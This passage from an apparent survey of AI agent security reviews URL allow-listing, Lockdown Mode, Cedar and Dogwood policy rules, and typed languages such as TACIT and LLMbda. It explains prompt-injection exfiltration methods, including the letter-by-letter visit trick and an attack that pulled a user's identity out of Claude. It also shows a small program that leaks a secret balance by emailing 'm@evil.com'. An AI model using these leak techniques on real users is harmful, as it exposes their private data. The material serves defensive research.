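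The rule works because an indexed address, such as a news article's, was public before the conversation started, so it is very unlikely to contain the user's secrets. An address that the model assembles from the user's data won't be in the index. In information-flow terms, OpenAI can treat every indexed address as Public without tracking how the model produced it. Addresses that the user types in a chat are also allowed during that chat, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, security researcher Johann Rehberger's summary of the company's technical paper.

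The gap is that a choice between public addresses can also reveal a secret. Rehberger described the trick in 2023, and OpenAI's paper acknowledges that it still works. An attacker with 36 indexed pages can assign one to each letter and digit, then have the model spell out a secret by visiting them in order. This is one of Denning's implicit flows, since the secret is never in any address. Ignoring timing, k visits to a choice of N pages can reveal up to

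k × log₂ N bits.

Encoding a six-digit login code takes six visits if there are ten pages to choose from, but only two if there are a thousand, because each visit can then represent three digits.

The trick is less reliable because browsers may store pages or request them in a different order. Rehberger suggests going further by stopping an agent from visiting the same address twice in a session. An attacker would then need more pages but could still get a little information out.

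A similar attack worked on Claude, whose browsing tool could originally open only addresses that came from the user, a search, or a page it had already read. The researcher Ayush Paul built a site that asked AI assistants to spell out their user's identity by following a link for each letter. He obtained the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic then stopped the tool from following links in pages it had fetched. Safe URL would have made the attack harder, because Paul's site generated its links as the agent followed them, so they wouldn't normally have been in an index.

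In March 2026, OpenAI said Safe URL was active in ChatGPT and also covered page visits and bookmarks in Atlas, and searches and page visits in Deep Research, its tool for writing long reports. OpenAI uses a related method for apps inside ChatGPT and for small programs that ChatGPT creates in Canvas, its document and code editor. These run in a sandbox that asks the user before any unexpected communication.

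OpenAI took a long time to reach this point. Rehberger reported the image attack in early 2023, and by his account there was little interest in fixing it. Microsoft fixed the same problem in Bing Chat that May. OpenAI added a first check in December 2023, but Rehberger found ways around it and noticed that the macOS and iOS apps didn't have it. He still considers incomplete adoption a risk, because developers in a large company may not know the check exists.

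Safe URL also controls only one sink. It doesn't stop a hostile page from making a summary wrong, or an agent from sending a private document through an email tool.

### Lockdown Mode and later changes

Users who want stronger protection can turn on Lockdown Mode, which OpenAI first offered to organisations in February 2026 and extended to personal accounts in June. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) describes how ordinary software limits or turns off features that could send data out, without relying on a model to judge whether a request looks suspicious. ChatGPT can then read only stored copies of web pages, which blocks the letter-by-letter trick because ChatGPT no longer contacts live websites. Lockdown Mode also disables Deep Research and agent mode.

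Willison liked this design because it removes one part of the lethal trifecta with controls that an attacker can't get around by persuading the model. He also inferred that ChatGPT's normal settings don't offer robust protection against a determined attacker. OpenAI presents the mode as an option for people who handle especially sensitive data, many of whom will have to give up the features that make ChatGPT an agent.

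OpenAI's description of the threat has also changed. The Decoder's *ChatGPT's new Lockdown Mode lets you disable web access and more* quoted a help page where OpenAI wrote that prompt injection "is not currently a major risk". By December 2026, OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* called it a known security risk for any AI system that processes untrusted content.

The August guide recommends stricter limits than most of OpenAI's consumer products have. It tells companies to treat everything an agent retrieves as untrusted, and never to rely on a reviewing model alone to block actions that must not happen automatically. Chrome's critic would fail the second requirement without the other layers of protection around it. The guide also advises treating each connected tool as a "capability grant", by which it means an approved permission that an administrator records and reviews, not an object capability.

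Lockdown Mode doesn't affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, and in company workspaces it doesn't automatically turn off connected apps. Administrators have to choose which apps and actions to allow, and OpenAI advises them to let an app write something only if they are confident that no attacker can see the result. FIDES can enforce a rule like that in code, but with Lockdown Mode an administrator has to work it out for each app.

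## Formal methods: from guaranteed-safety proposals to Amazon's checked permission rules

An administrator writing rules for dozens of apps can easily end up with two that contradict each other, or one that allows far more than intended. Formal methods can find many such mistakes, and Amazon has used them this way in a product for agents since December 2025. The best-known proposal for formal methods in AI safety has a much more ambitious goal, a mathematical guarantee that an AI system won't cause unacceptable harm in the world.

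### Guaranteed safe AI

Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024) set out this proposal in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*. The 17 authors include the prominent AI researchers Yoshua Bengio and Stuart Russell, as well as formal-methods specialists such as Sanjit Seshia and Clark Barrett. They were thinking mainly about future systems that might be more intelligent than people, rather than about email assistants.

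Their approach adds three things to the AI system. A world model describes mathematically how the system affects its surroundings. A safety specification defines which effects are acceptable. A verifier then produces a proof, which other people can check, that the system meets the specification according to the world model. The strongest kind of proof covers every possible input. A weaker kind limits the probability of harm:

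Pr(the outcome is unacceptable, according to the world model) ≤ ε,

where ε is the level of risk that society will accept. Dalrymple and colleagues would ideally have the public decide what counts as acceptable through some kind of collective deliberation.

They argue mainly that testing can't give this much assurance. OpenAI tested ChatGPT for months, but users got around its safety measures within a day of its release. Someone could also hide a backdoor in a model that no practical test would find, and a deceptive system might behave well only when it detects a test. As a comparison, Dalrymple and colleagues note that about a quarter of bridges built in the 1870s collapsed within ten years, but fewer than 0.4% per decade failed once engineers had better theory.

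They accept that tests can produce numerical estimates of risk. If a self-driving car covers a million miles without a test driver stepping in, its failure rate is probably below one in a million miles. (The result gives 95% confidence only that the rate is below about three in a million.) But the estimate assumes that driving conditions stay the same, and people might drive more aggressively around these cars once they get used to them.

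The difficulty is that someone has to write down a lot correctly before the verifier can start. To prove that the mail assistant never harms anyone, a developer would need a mathematical definition of harm. They would also need a world model that covers what a colleague might do with a contract, and nobody has a reliable one.

Dalrymple and colleagues acknowledge that harm and causation are hard to formalise, but reply that theories of both exist, that developers can sometimes define harm more narrowly for one setting, and that a verifier can use several specifications at once. Where the world model is uncertain, they want it to overestimate what could happen. This keeps the proof valid but can make the verifier too restrictive, a problem similar to label creep. If the model allows for almost anything a colleague might do, the verifier may not be able to approve sending any email.

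The argument against testing also partly applies to the world model, because people can only check its accuracy by observing the world. The model still has the advantage that its assumptions are written down, so others can criticise them. The approach looks most promising where engineers already have good mathematical models, as they do for electricity grids.

Dalrymple worked at the UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA), which committed £59 million to its Safeguarded AI programme. The plan was to build a "gatekeeper" that would let another AI system act only within limits it could prove safe, and to test it in areas such as energy and healthcare. No general-purpose agent on the market is known to have such a guarantee.

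### Cedar, a language designed for analysis

Much of this difficulty disappears if the aim is only to control which tool calls an agent can make. The specification is then a set of permission rules. Checking a rule that forbids refunds of $200 or more doesn't require a world model, because the rule concerns the call and not its consequences.

Amazon Web Services (AWS), Amazon's cloud business, already had a language for such rules. It released Cedar as open source in May 2023, mainly for ordinary apps whose users need different permissions. A Cedar request identifies who is asking, what action they want to take and on what resource, along with details such as an amount of money. Each rule either permits or forbids some requests, and Cedar combines the rules like this:

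allowed = (at least one permit rule matches) and (no forbid rule matches).

Cedar refuses any request that no rule explicitly permits, as Saltzer and Schroeder recommended. A forbid rule overrides any number of permit rules, and the order of the rules makes no difference. A security team can add a rule forbidding refunds on old orders and know that no permit rule will override it.

Cedar has no loops and stores nothing between requests. Denning and Denning had shown that no procedure can decide exactly which ordinary programs are secure, and Cedar's designers avoided that problem by leaving out the features that cause it. A tool can translate any set of Cedar rules into a logical formula and pass it to a solver, a program that either finds values that make the formula true or proves that there are none.

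For example, AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* describes a shop that gives bulk discounts on orders of at least 50 items, except for limited-edition products. Someone changes the exception so that it covers only limited-edition orders of more than 200 items. The extra condition makes the rule look stricter. To check, a tool has the solver look for an order that the new rule allows and the old one doesn't. If q is the number of items, such an order has to satisfy

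q ≥ 50 and limited edition and q ≤ 200.

An order for 73 limited-edition items fits, so the change makes the rule looser. A developer who tested only a few ordinary orders might have missed this. The solver is guaranteed to find it because it treats q as an unknown and covers every value at once.

The same method finds several other kinds of mistake:

| Mistake | What the solver looks for | Result that reveals the mistake |
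|---|---|---|
| A rule that can never apply | A request that matches the rule | There is none |
| A rule that always applies | A request that doesn't match the rule | There is none |
| A forbid rule that cancels a permit rule | A request that matches the permit rule but not the forbid rule | There is none |
| A change that loosens the rules | A request allowed only after the change | There is one |

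Cedar came out of a long effort at AWS. Byron Cook, who had earlier worked on proving that programs terminate, founded the company's Automated Reasoning Group more than a decade ago, according to Software Engineering Daily's *Formal Methods as Agent Guardrails*. The group laid the foundations for IAM Access Analyzer, which uses logic to work out who can reach a customer's data. In All Things Distributed's *A chat with Byron Cook on automated reasoning and trust in AI* (2026), Cook mentions Bedrock Guardrails, which can filter out some of a model's false statements after it has produced them.

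Cedar's designers included Michael Hicks, who had been a programming-languages professor at the University of Maryland, and Emina Torlak, who had built tools that make solvers easier for programmers to use. Cedar is also linked to the guaranteed-safety proposal through Barrett, who helps lead the development of cvc5, the solver Cedar's analysis tools use.

The team also applied formal methods to Cedar itself. AWS's *Introducing Cedar, an open-source language for access control* (2023) explains that engineers wrote a formal model of the part that makes decisions and proved the model correct. Customers run a separate program, written in Rust, which the engineers test against the model. The proof therefore applies to that program only if the tests haven't missed a difference between the two.

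Other companies have started to use the language. In November 2026, NVIDIA's OpenShell project, which makes sandboxes for agents, announced that it was adopting Cedar for its rules. Raman (2026), in *Cedar as the policy language in OpenShell*, says one reason is that comparing Cedar policies gives a definite answer.

### A refund rule in AgentCore

AWS previewed Policy in AgentCore on 2 December 2025 and made it generally available on 3 March 2026. AgentCore is the company's platform for running agents. An agent's tool calls go through a gateway, a reference monitor very much like Anderson's, which checks each call against the customer's Cedar rules before it reaches the tool.

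Marc Brooker, an AWS engineer who works on agent safety, calls this arrangement a box. He argues in *Agent Safety is a Box* that controls inside an agent face a hard trade-off, because people want agents to be flexible and flexible systems are difficult to reason about. With the box, a developer can leave the model's planning unrestricted and control only its actions. AgentCore lets the agent send network traffic only to the gateway. A company that uses the gateway with an agent running elsewhere has to block the other routes itself.

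Suppose a shop has an agent that handles refunds. The two rules below are simplified from AWS's examples.

```
permit process_refund
when { user.role == "refund-agent" && input.amount < 200 };

forbid process_refund
when { input.orderDate + 90 days < now };
```

The gateway would decide these calls as follows:

| User's role | Amount | Age of order | Decision | Reason |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| refund-agent | $120 | 10 days | Allowed | The permit rule matches |
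| refund-agent | $450 | 10 days | Refused | No permit rule matches |
| sales | $120 | 10 days | Refused | No permit rule matches |
| refund-agent | $120 | 100 days | Refused | The forbid rule overrides the permit rule |

The second call fails regardless of why the model requested $450. A customer may have written a persuasive message, or the model may have misread the price, but neither affects the comparison of 450 with 200.

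People who don't want to learn Cedar can describe a rule in plain English and have a model draft it. AgentCore first checks that the draft refers to real tools and arguments, then runs the solver. In one of AWS's examples, a faulty draft permits refunds when

tier = "Gold" and tier = "Platinum".

The writer meant customers in either tier, but no customer can be in both, so the solver proves that the rule will never permit anything. AgentCore returns the error to the model, which tries again. When the customer attaches the rules to a gateway, AgentCore checks them together. If one rule permits refunds under $100 for gold customers and another forbids refunds under $500 for the same customers, AgentCore rejects the set and explains the conflict.

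AWS's *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore adds quality evaluations and policy controls* describes another way to find mistakes, in which the gateway logs its decisions without enforcing them. Before enforcing a new rule, a developer can see which real calls it would have blocked.

The gateway also uses the rules to shorten the list of tools it gives the agent. If the rules forbid every possible call to a tool, the gateway leaves that tool off the list, and the model never reads its description. This saves tokens and should prevent some pointless calls.

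AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026) says companies can use the feature in thirteen regions, but does not report how many attacks or mistakes the rules have stopped.

### Rules that pass every check and are still wrong

If someone types 2000 instead of 200 in the refund rule, the solver will find nothing wrong, because the rule still allows some requests, refuses others, and doesn't conflict with any other rule. The solver can't check whether the rule matches what the shop's owner wanted.

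The 90-day rule has a less obvious flaw. The model writes the order date as one of the call's arguments, whereas the user's role comes from a login token the model can't change. An attacker who tricks the model into supplying a recent date can get a refund on an old order, unless the refund tool looks up the real date. The refund amount is safer because the tool pays out whatever amount the call contains, so a false number gains the attacker nothing. AWS points out the difference between data from the token and data from the model in its bulk-discount example, where the model also supplies the list of product types.

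Even with an accurate date, the attacker can ask for a $150 refund they aren't owed. The rules limit the size of each refund but can't determine whether it is justified. The policies in Costa and colleagues' FIDES could refuse the call because untrusted text had influenced it, but these Cedar rules don't track that influence.

The agent could also make a hundred refunds of $199, for a total of $19,900. Cedar would allow them all, because it evaluates each request separately. Brooker illustrates the box with a shop that never refunds more than the purchase price and gives only one refund per order, but his sample rule only requires the amount to be under $500. A rule of one refund per order depends on earlier refunds, so Cedar can't enforce it unless other software looks up the history and adds it to the request.

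### Dogwood and rules about the past

In August 2026 AWS released Dogwood, a language whose rules can depend on an agent's earlier actions. Any Cedar rule is also a Dogwood rule. Its designers included Brooker, Joseph Tassarotti of the Automated Reasoning Group, and Jean-Baptiste Tristan, who had co-written the company's explanation of why AgentCore uses Cedar. AWS announced Dogwood as "runtime verification for AI agents". Runtime verification is the branch of formal methods that checks a program's behaviour while it runs.

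The gateway records one event when the agent requests a tool call and another for the outcome. A Dogwood rule can depend on whether a certain event happened within a period such as the last hour, how many times it happened, or what the amounts add up to. Before each decision, the software works these out from the record and adds them to the request, which Cedar then evaluates as usual.

Under a rule in AWS's *Temporal policies*, an agent may sell shares only if an approval for the same stock and number of shares was granted within the past hour. This catches an agent that skips the approval or changes the number afterwards. But the rule as printed lets an agent reuse an approval, so an agent approved to sell 100 shares could sell 100 several times within the hour. A developer who wants one sale per approval has to add a limit on the number of sales.

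InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* (2026) picks out another trap from the announcement. Suppose a company wants to cap transfers at $5,000, and its agent requests three transfers of $2,000 at the same moment. If the rule adds up completed transfers, the total is still zero when the gateway checks each request, so all three go through and the agent spends $6,000. If the rule adds up requests instead, the totals are

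$2,000, $4,000, $6,000,

and the gateway refuses the third. The two versions of the rule differ by one word. Programmers know this kind of bug well from banking software, but someone who describes the cap in plain English probably won't think of it.

Dogwood can also stop an agent from contacting outsiders after it has opened a confidential file. This is a simple version of information-flow control, and it suffers from label creep too. Dogwood records calls and their results, but not which text the model used to write a message, so the rule also blocks harmless messages.

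The record also covers only one session. The software that calls the gateway chooses the session's identifier, and AWS warns that a new session starts a new count. If each chat with the refund agent is its own session, a customer who opens ten chats gets ten allowances. An attack spread over two days could get through the same way, like the invoice that an agent saves on Monday and pays on Tuesday. Even within one session, no condition can look back more than 24 hours, so a monthly spending limit has to go in the payment system.

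Other limits make Dogwood awkward for large companies. Each set can have up to 25 rules of this kind, and each rule can have up to three conditions about the past. Changing one of these rules ends the sessions in progress, because the recorded history may not fit the new rules.

The biggest drawback is that Cedar's analysis doesn't yet work on conditions about the past, even though rules with such conditions best describe what companies want from an agent. A customer who adds these conditions loses the formal check on that set of rules, and AWS gave this as its reason for making Dogwood a separate language. The gateway still enforces the rules exactly as written, but no solver will detect a rule that can never apply.

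Running Dogwood outside AgentCore takes more work. According to InfoQ, the free interpreter released in August was meant for trying out the language, and a real system would need trustworthy timestamps, secure storage for the event log and strict separation between customers. AWS has since released a separate local engine.

### Checking the whole plan first

Dogwood decides at each call, after earlier calls have taken effect. If the third step of a task breaks a rule, the agent has already done the first two, and someone may have to undo them.

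Erik Meijer, a programming-language designer who helped create Microsoft's query language LINQ, proposed checking an agent's whole plan before running any of it. In *Guardians of the Agents* (ACM Queue, 2025), the model writes its plan as a program, a verifier checks the program against safety rules, and the harness runs it only if it passes. Before the mail assistant opens a private file, the verifier could reject any plan that might send that file to an outsider.

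This catches harmful sequences, and verification doesn't depend on trusting the model that wrote the plan. As with CaMeL, the drawback is that the model has to write the program before the emails' contents are available to it. Other researchers later produced machine-checked proofs of noninterference for programs like these.

### Models that write the rules

All these systems need someone to write good rules. Companies already have many, but mostly in English, in handbooks and contracts. AWS's *Authoring Dogwood policies from natural language in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* describes a tool that uses models to translate whole documents into Dogwood rules, and calls the results "syntactically and semantically correct". Software can check the syntax, but a person has to judge whether a rule means what the handbook's writer meant.

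Amazon also writes that checking drafts with a solver significantly improves their accuracy, but it doesn't say by how much in its explanation of AgentCore's use of Cedar. The best published numbers come from AgentSpec, an earlier academic system described in *Customizable Runtime Enforcement for Safe and Reliable LLM Agents* (2025). An AgentSpec rule has a trigger (such as a bank transfer), a condition (such as an amount over a limit), and a response, which can be to ask the user or to have the model reconsider its plan. Asking the model is the weaker choice, since an attacker who has fooled it once may fool it again.

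AgentSpec, using rules written by people, prevented more than 90% of unsafe actions by agents that run code and all hazardous actions by simulated household robots. It also kept simulated self-driving cars within traffic laws. Its checks took only milliseconds. These results mostly show that people can write good rules for dangers they already know about.

The researchers then had OpenAI's o1 write the rules. Its rules identified 87% of the risky code and prevented the cars from breaking the law in five of eight scenarios. For the household robots, about 96% of the actions the rules flagged were dangerous, but the rules missed 29% of the dangerous actions. Newer models would probably write better rules than o1, but missing rules are still the hardest errors to notice.

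Cedar refuses requests by default, which helps here because somebody will complain if a model omits a permit rule. But a permit rule that is too broad, or a missing forbid rule, causes no complaints.

On 1 December 2026, AWS announced a preview of its newest service, Greenlight, which extends this approach. A model drafts rules from a company's procedures, security standards and records of past tool calls, and a solver looks for conflicts and for routes to resources the agent shouldn't reach. Before accepting a change, the company can see which recorded calls the change would have blocked. This would help with the mistyped refund limit, because a manager who expected the rule to stop a $450 refund could see that it wouldn't have.

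Greenlight's proofs cover every case because the solver leaves the details of the request unknown. They concern only the calls that the rules allow, not whether the agent will do its job well. Some descriptions make the proofs sound stronger than they are. Wheatley (2026), in *AWS greenlights autonomous AI agents to take control*, reports that a rule shown to hold in one scenario can be trusted in any situation, but a solver doesn't generalise from one case.

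Pogorelec (2026) reports in *AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules* that LoanLogics, an early customer selling mortgage-auditing technology, wants to check its agents against thousands of policies from government agencies, investors and banks. Models can draft these rules quickly, but people still have to approve them, and thousands of approvals could tire a compliance team just as permission requests tire users. LoanLogics and Delta Air Lines were still planning to use the service when Pogorelec wrote.

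## 2026: typed languages and machine-checked proofs for agents

Amazon's gateway checks an agent's tool calls one at a time, while Meijer wanted to check the whole plan before any of it ran. His idea works only if the model writes its plan as a program, which many agents already did by 2026. CaMeL's privileged model writes restricted Python, agents that use Cloudflare's Code Mode write JavaScript, and coding agents routinely write programs. This gave programming-language researchers something they already knew how to check. A compiler can read a program's text and rule out some behaviour on every possible run, but nobody can do this for tool calls that the model hasn't chosen yet.

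The field also had experience with untrusted code. Browsers run scripts from strangers' websites, and those scripts can generate more code as they run, so researchers who tracked information flow in JavaScript had already dealt with code that doesn't exist until just before it runs. An agent's program is similar, since no person has reviewed it and a stranger's email may have influenced it.

Strict languages may also suit models better than they suited people. Few programmers want to fix compiler errors about labels, but when a model's program fails to compile, the harness can send the model the error message and get a corrected version within seconds.

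### TACIT: a compiler that tracks capabilities

Martin Odersky, who designed the language Scala, and his group at EPFL had spent several years on capture checking, which extends Scala's types to record the capabilities a piece of code can use. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) applies capture checking to agents in a system called TACIT. The capabilities are object capabilities in Miller's sense, such as an object that gives access to one folder.

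Suppose the mail assistant holds `reply`, an object that can send a message in one thread. A function that takes some text and sends it through `reply` has the type

`String ->{reply} Unit`

The braces list the capabilities the function uses, and `Unit` means the function returns nothing useful. A function that only counts the letters in a text has the type `String -> Int`, with no braces. Such a function is pure, so it can't send, write or print anything. The compiler works out these lists itself and rejects code that uses a capability its type doesn't allow.

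TACIT relies on this to protect secrets. When the agent's program reads a file from a folder the user has marked as classified, it gets a `Classified[String]`, a sealed wrapper around the text. The program can't open the wrapper, but it can pass a function to the wrapper's `map` method, which accepts only pure functions. `map` applies the function to the text and seals the result.

```
val contract = readClassified("contract.txt")
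contract.map(text => text.length)
contract.map(text => reply.send(text))
```

The compiler accepts the second line, which produces a sealed number. It rejects the third because the function uses `reply`, and TACIT then runs none of the program. If customer records are classified, a TACIT program with capabilities for reading them and for posting publicly still can't post the records. Cloudflare's bindings don't prevent a program with both capabilities from doing so.

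The model that writes the program never receives the contract's text either. If the program prints a classified value, the user's terminal shows the real text, but the model gets only `Classified(****)`. For tasks that require reading the text, such as summarizing it, the program can pass the sealed text to a second model that the user trusts, perhaps one on the user's computer, and get a sealed answer back.

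TACIT's design looks like the dual-LLM pattern with the trust reversed. The planning model is untrusted, so the secrets should stay safe even if the model's provider is hostile or the user's own prompt is an attack. CaMeL doesn't protect against either case.

Capabilities can also expire. A program can open a folder for the length of one block of code, and the compiler rejects the program if anything that leaves the block could still use the folder. With Miller's forwarding objects, the owner has to cut off access while the program runs.

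Ordinary Scala has features that would defeat all this, such as casts, which tell the compiler to treat a value as a different type, and reflection, which lets a program call code that the compiler hasn't checked. TACIT compiles the agent's code in "safe mode", which bans both and limits the program to approved libraries. Library authors can approve their own code by hand if it uses an unsafe feature harmlessly, but the compiler doesn't check that the use is harmless.

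TACIT doesn't keep untrusted text away from the planning model, so an ordinary email can still change what the agent does next, as long as the new action stays within the agent's capabilities. If the agent holds `reply` and nobody marked the contract as classified, it can still send the contract to the stranger. TACIT's protection also doesn't extend to programs outside Scala. An agent with permission to run a command-line tool can do whatever that tool does, so Odersky and colleagues recommend adding a short list of permitted commands and a sandbox.

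### What the TACIT experiments measured

The team set up a software project with a folder of passwords, keys and confidential documents. They paired 12 ordinary tasks with 10 injected attacks. They also wrote 11 malicious requests, in which the user asked for the secrets directly or posed as someone with authority, such as a system administrator. The table shows how often the agent's output contained no secrets.

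| Model | Test | With `Classified` | Without it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 injection trials | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 injection trials | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 27.3% |

The perfect scores are unsurprising, because the test counts the kind of leak that the compiler forbids. The types made little difference against injections, since Sonnet resisted every injection without them and MiniMax failed only three times. They mattered much more when the user was the attacker. With the types in place, Sonnet still completed 99.2% of the ordinary tasks, including summaries of classified reports, and MiniMax completed 90.0%.

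AgentDojo counted one attack in 1,926 trials as successful, another case in which the agent quoted a hotel review word for word. The comparison included no unprotected agent, so it can't separate the effect of the types from the models' own resistance. Odersky and colleagues describe TACIT's success on user tasks as comparable to CaMeL's, but with o4-mini-high, one of the two models, TACIT did worse in all four settings. In the workspace setting it completed 52.9% of tasks, while CaMeL had completed 81.4%.

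The team also tested whether models can write this kind of Scala, since there is little of it to learn from. On τ²-bench, which simulates customer service for an airline and a shop, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with typed Scala than with ordinary tool calls. The researchers attribute the gains to the structured results and the compiler's error messages. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of real software bugs, MiniMax solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it.

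At most 7.9% of the customer-service programs needed a retry, and one or two attempts usually fixed them. These numbers suggest that the language isn't a big obstacle for models, but they don't measure how many useful tasks a strict policy would block.

The same group soon extended the idea in *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), which lets a developer write `agent[T]("task")` anywhere in a Scala program, where `T` is the type of answer the program needs. When the program reaches that call, a model writes code to fill it in, and the compiler checks the new code against the surrounding code before it runs.

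In one LACUNA example, the model has to subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return the new number. Its code subtracts correctly but returns text instead of a number. The compiler rejects all of the code, so the balance stays at 100, whereas an unchecked Python program would have changed the balance before failing. LACUNA solved 76.0% of 392 τ²-bench tasks, about as many as an ordinary agent.

### Language-based agent control in Haskell

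*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) starts from the choice most agent frameworks force on developers between fixed tools and a code interpreter. Fixed tools are easy to control, but the agent can't combine them freely. A code interpreter lets the agent do almost anything, including things the developer wanted to prevent. Loris D'Antoni and Nadia Polikarpova, at the University of California San Diego, had both worked on program synthesis, in which software writes programs to fit a specification. Here a language model writes the program, and a type serves as a simple specification.

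The developer writes the whole application in Haskell and calls a function named `agent` wherever a model should take over. The type at that point limits what the model's program may do. For instance, an online calculator might need a whole number, so the type is `Int`. If a visitor asks the calculator to delete all the files on the server and then compute the factorial of 5, the model may write a program that does both. Deleting files is an effect, so the program doesn't have the type `Int`, and the compiler rejects it. The design uses Safe Haskell, a restricted form of the language without loopholes such as `unsafePerformIO`.

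Most agents need some effects. Zhou and colleagues give the example of an agent that compiles bibliographies and may include only entries from DBLP, a database of computer-science papers. The developer defines a type for programs whose only effects are searching DBLP, fetching an entry and adding a fetched entry to a file. Fetched entries have the type `Trusted Bib`, and only the developer's library can create a value of that type. The model's program can sort and filter entries freely, but it can't add an invented one to the file.

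In a test with 100 topics, none of this agent's 925 citations were false. An ordinary agent with a search tool got the authors, year or identifier wrong in 19 of its 1,002 citations. The type can't ensure that the cited papers are relevant.

Unlike CaMeL's planner, this agent can change its plan as it goes. A program can fetch a result and call `agent` again with that result in the prompt. The second model can react to the result, but its program must fit the same type as the first or a stricter one.

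Zhou and colleagues prove that any property the host language guarantees for every well-typed program also holds for programs that contain agent calls. The proof replaces each call with an ordinary function that queries the model, checks the returned code and runs it. That code may contain further agent calls, but their depth is limited, so the replacement eventually ends. The proof holds whatever the model returns. The theorem lets developers reuse protections that Haskell libraries already provide, but it doesn't create new ones.

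One of these is LIO, an information-flow library that Deian Stefan, Alejandro Russo and colleagues introduced in 2011. Like FIDES, LIO keeps one label covering everything the program has read so far and blocks writes that the label doesn't permit. It can also run part of a program separately and return a sealed result, without changing the label on the rest of the program.

If the separate part contains an agent call, the result is the dual-LLM pattern, except that the inner agent keeps its tools until it reads something that rules them out. LIO checks labels while the program runs, so a program that compiles can still stop partway through. The types ensure that the program can't bypass these checks.

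The team compared its implementation, ELBA, with CaMeL on the 21 tasks in AgentDojo's Slack setting. The table shows how many tasks each system completed when not under attack.

| Model | ELBA, policies on | CaMeL, policies on | ELBA, policies off | CaMeL, policies off |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 10 | 5 | 18 | 15 |
| Opus 4.8 | 9 | 6 | 16 | 16 |
| GPT 5.4 | 10 | 5 | 16 | 17 |
| Sonnet 5 | 8 | 4 | 14 | 13 |

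With policies on, ELBA completed roughly twice as many tasks as CaMeL, but failed almost half of the tasks it could complete without them. The two systems enforced different policies, so the difference isn't due only to their designs. An earlier version of the Haskell system, called TypeGuard, had completed 8 tasks to CaMeL's 7. ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL because it calls the model again whenever it needs to react to data.

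The models ignored every attack on both systems, even with the policies off. The researchers therefore simulated the worst case by giving any ELBA sub-agent that received an attack the attacker's text as its only instruction. Between 16% and 42% of attacks then succeeded without policies, depending on the model, and none of 2,940 succeeded with them. AgentDojo counted 29 of these as successes, but in each one the agent had only opened a fixed web address, which leaked nothing. This tests a harness better than waiting for a model to make a mistake, because the result depends much less on how well current models resist attacks.

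### A leak through a branch that doesn't run

Garby, Gordon and Sands began with faults in existing designs. David Sands had worked on the theory of information flow for many years, and Andrew Gordon on functional and probabilistic programming languages. In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (2026), the July version of their paper on the LLMbda calculus, they describe a program that gets a secret past CaMeL's tracking. In simplified form, it looks like this:

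```
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The balance is Secret, and both variables start out Public. CaMeL marks a variable as Secret when the program changes it inside a branch that depends on a secret. The table shows the program running on two accounts.

| Step | Balance above the threshold | Balance below the threshold |
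|---|---|---|
| `tmp` after the third line | False, Secret | True, Public |
| `rich` after the fourth line | True, Public | False, Public |
| Last line | Sends the email | Sends nothing |

The email goes out only if the balance is high, so its arrival reveals the secret. But when the balance is high, the program skips the assignment in the fourth line, and CaMeL can't use an assignment that never runs to mark a variable. `rich` is therefore Public when CaMeL reaches the last line, and the policy allows the email.

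This is one of Denning's implicit flows, and the example goes back to a 1974 paper by Fenton. Denning's compiler would have caught it, because it checks every branch. A system that only monitors the program as it runs needs another rule. In 2009, Thomas Austin and Cormac Flanagan proposed stopping the program before it changes something Public inside a Secret branch. In this example, their rule would stop the program at the third line if the balance is high.

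A stranger can't easily exploit this flaw through an email, because the email can't change the program. CaMeL's privileged model would have to write these odd lines by mistake or because the user had pasted in a malicious request. A simpler bug seems more worrying in practice, because ordinary programs could trigger it. When a program inserted an untrusted value into longer text, such as a name into "Dear ...", CaMeL treated the value as trusted.

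Garby and colleagues also found a leak outside the interpreter. When a program fails, CaMeL tries again in a loop of ordinary Python, which has no tracking. Whether a policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can leak one bit. One bit would be tolerable, but the loop can repeat the leak with a different question each time, and twenty yes-or-no answers are enough to identify any whole number up to about a million. CaMeL censors some error messages to limit this leak, but there is no formal guarantee that this works.

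FIDES's designers openly chose to ignore implicit flows and to let developers accept untrusted values that have only a few possibilities. Garby and colleagues consider each choice defensible, but object that a reviewer who looks at a particular run can't tell an intended exception from a real leak. Both sides accept that agents need exceptions, but Garby and colleagues want each one to appear in the program, where someone can find it.

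### The LLMbda calculus

Their own design is a small programming language based on the lambda calculus, a minimal language of functions. Every value has a label, and so does the conversation with the model. The conversation takes on the labels of all the messages sent to the model. The language has three operations for conversations: `@` sends a prompt and returns the model's answer, `fork` runs code with a copy of the conversation and then discards the copy, and `clear` empties the conversation.

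These are enough to build a quarantined model without adding one to the design:

```
fork (let _ = clear in @("Summarise this email: " + email))
```

The program copies the conversation, empties the copy, asks for the summary and throws the copy away. The stranger's email never enters the main conversation. The summary is labeled Untrusted, so `send_email` can reject it. A developer can use this pattern for one step and a normal conversation for the next, and the labels apply throughout.

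The model may answer with more code, which runs with the label of the conversation that produced it. If the model wrote the code after reading the stranger's email, everything the code does is labeled Untrusted, whatever the code contains.

An exception requires the command `endorse`, which raises a value's integrity but can't make a secret public. The command has no effect inside code that is itself Untrusted, so an attacker gains nothing by persuading a model to write `endorse` everywhere. An attacker can get around this restriction if the program has already endorsed the attacker's text by mistake and then builds code from it. Garby and colleagues offer a stricter version that permanently marks endorsed values and refuses to endorse them twice.

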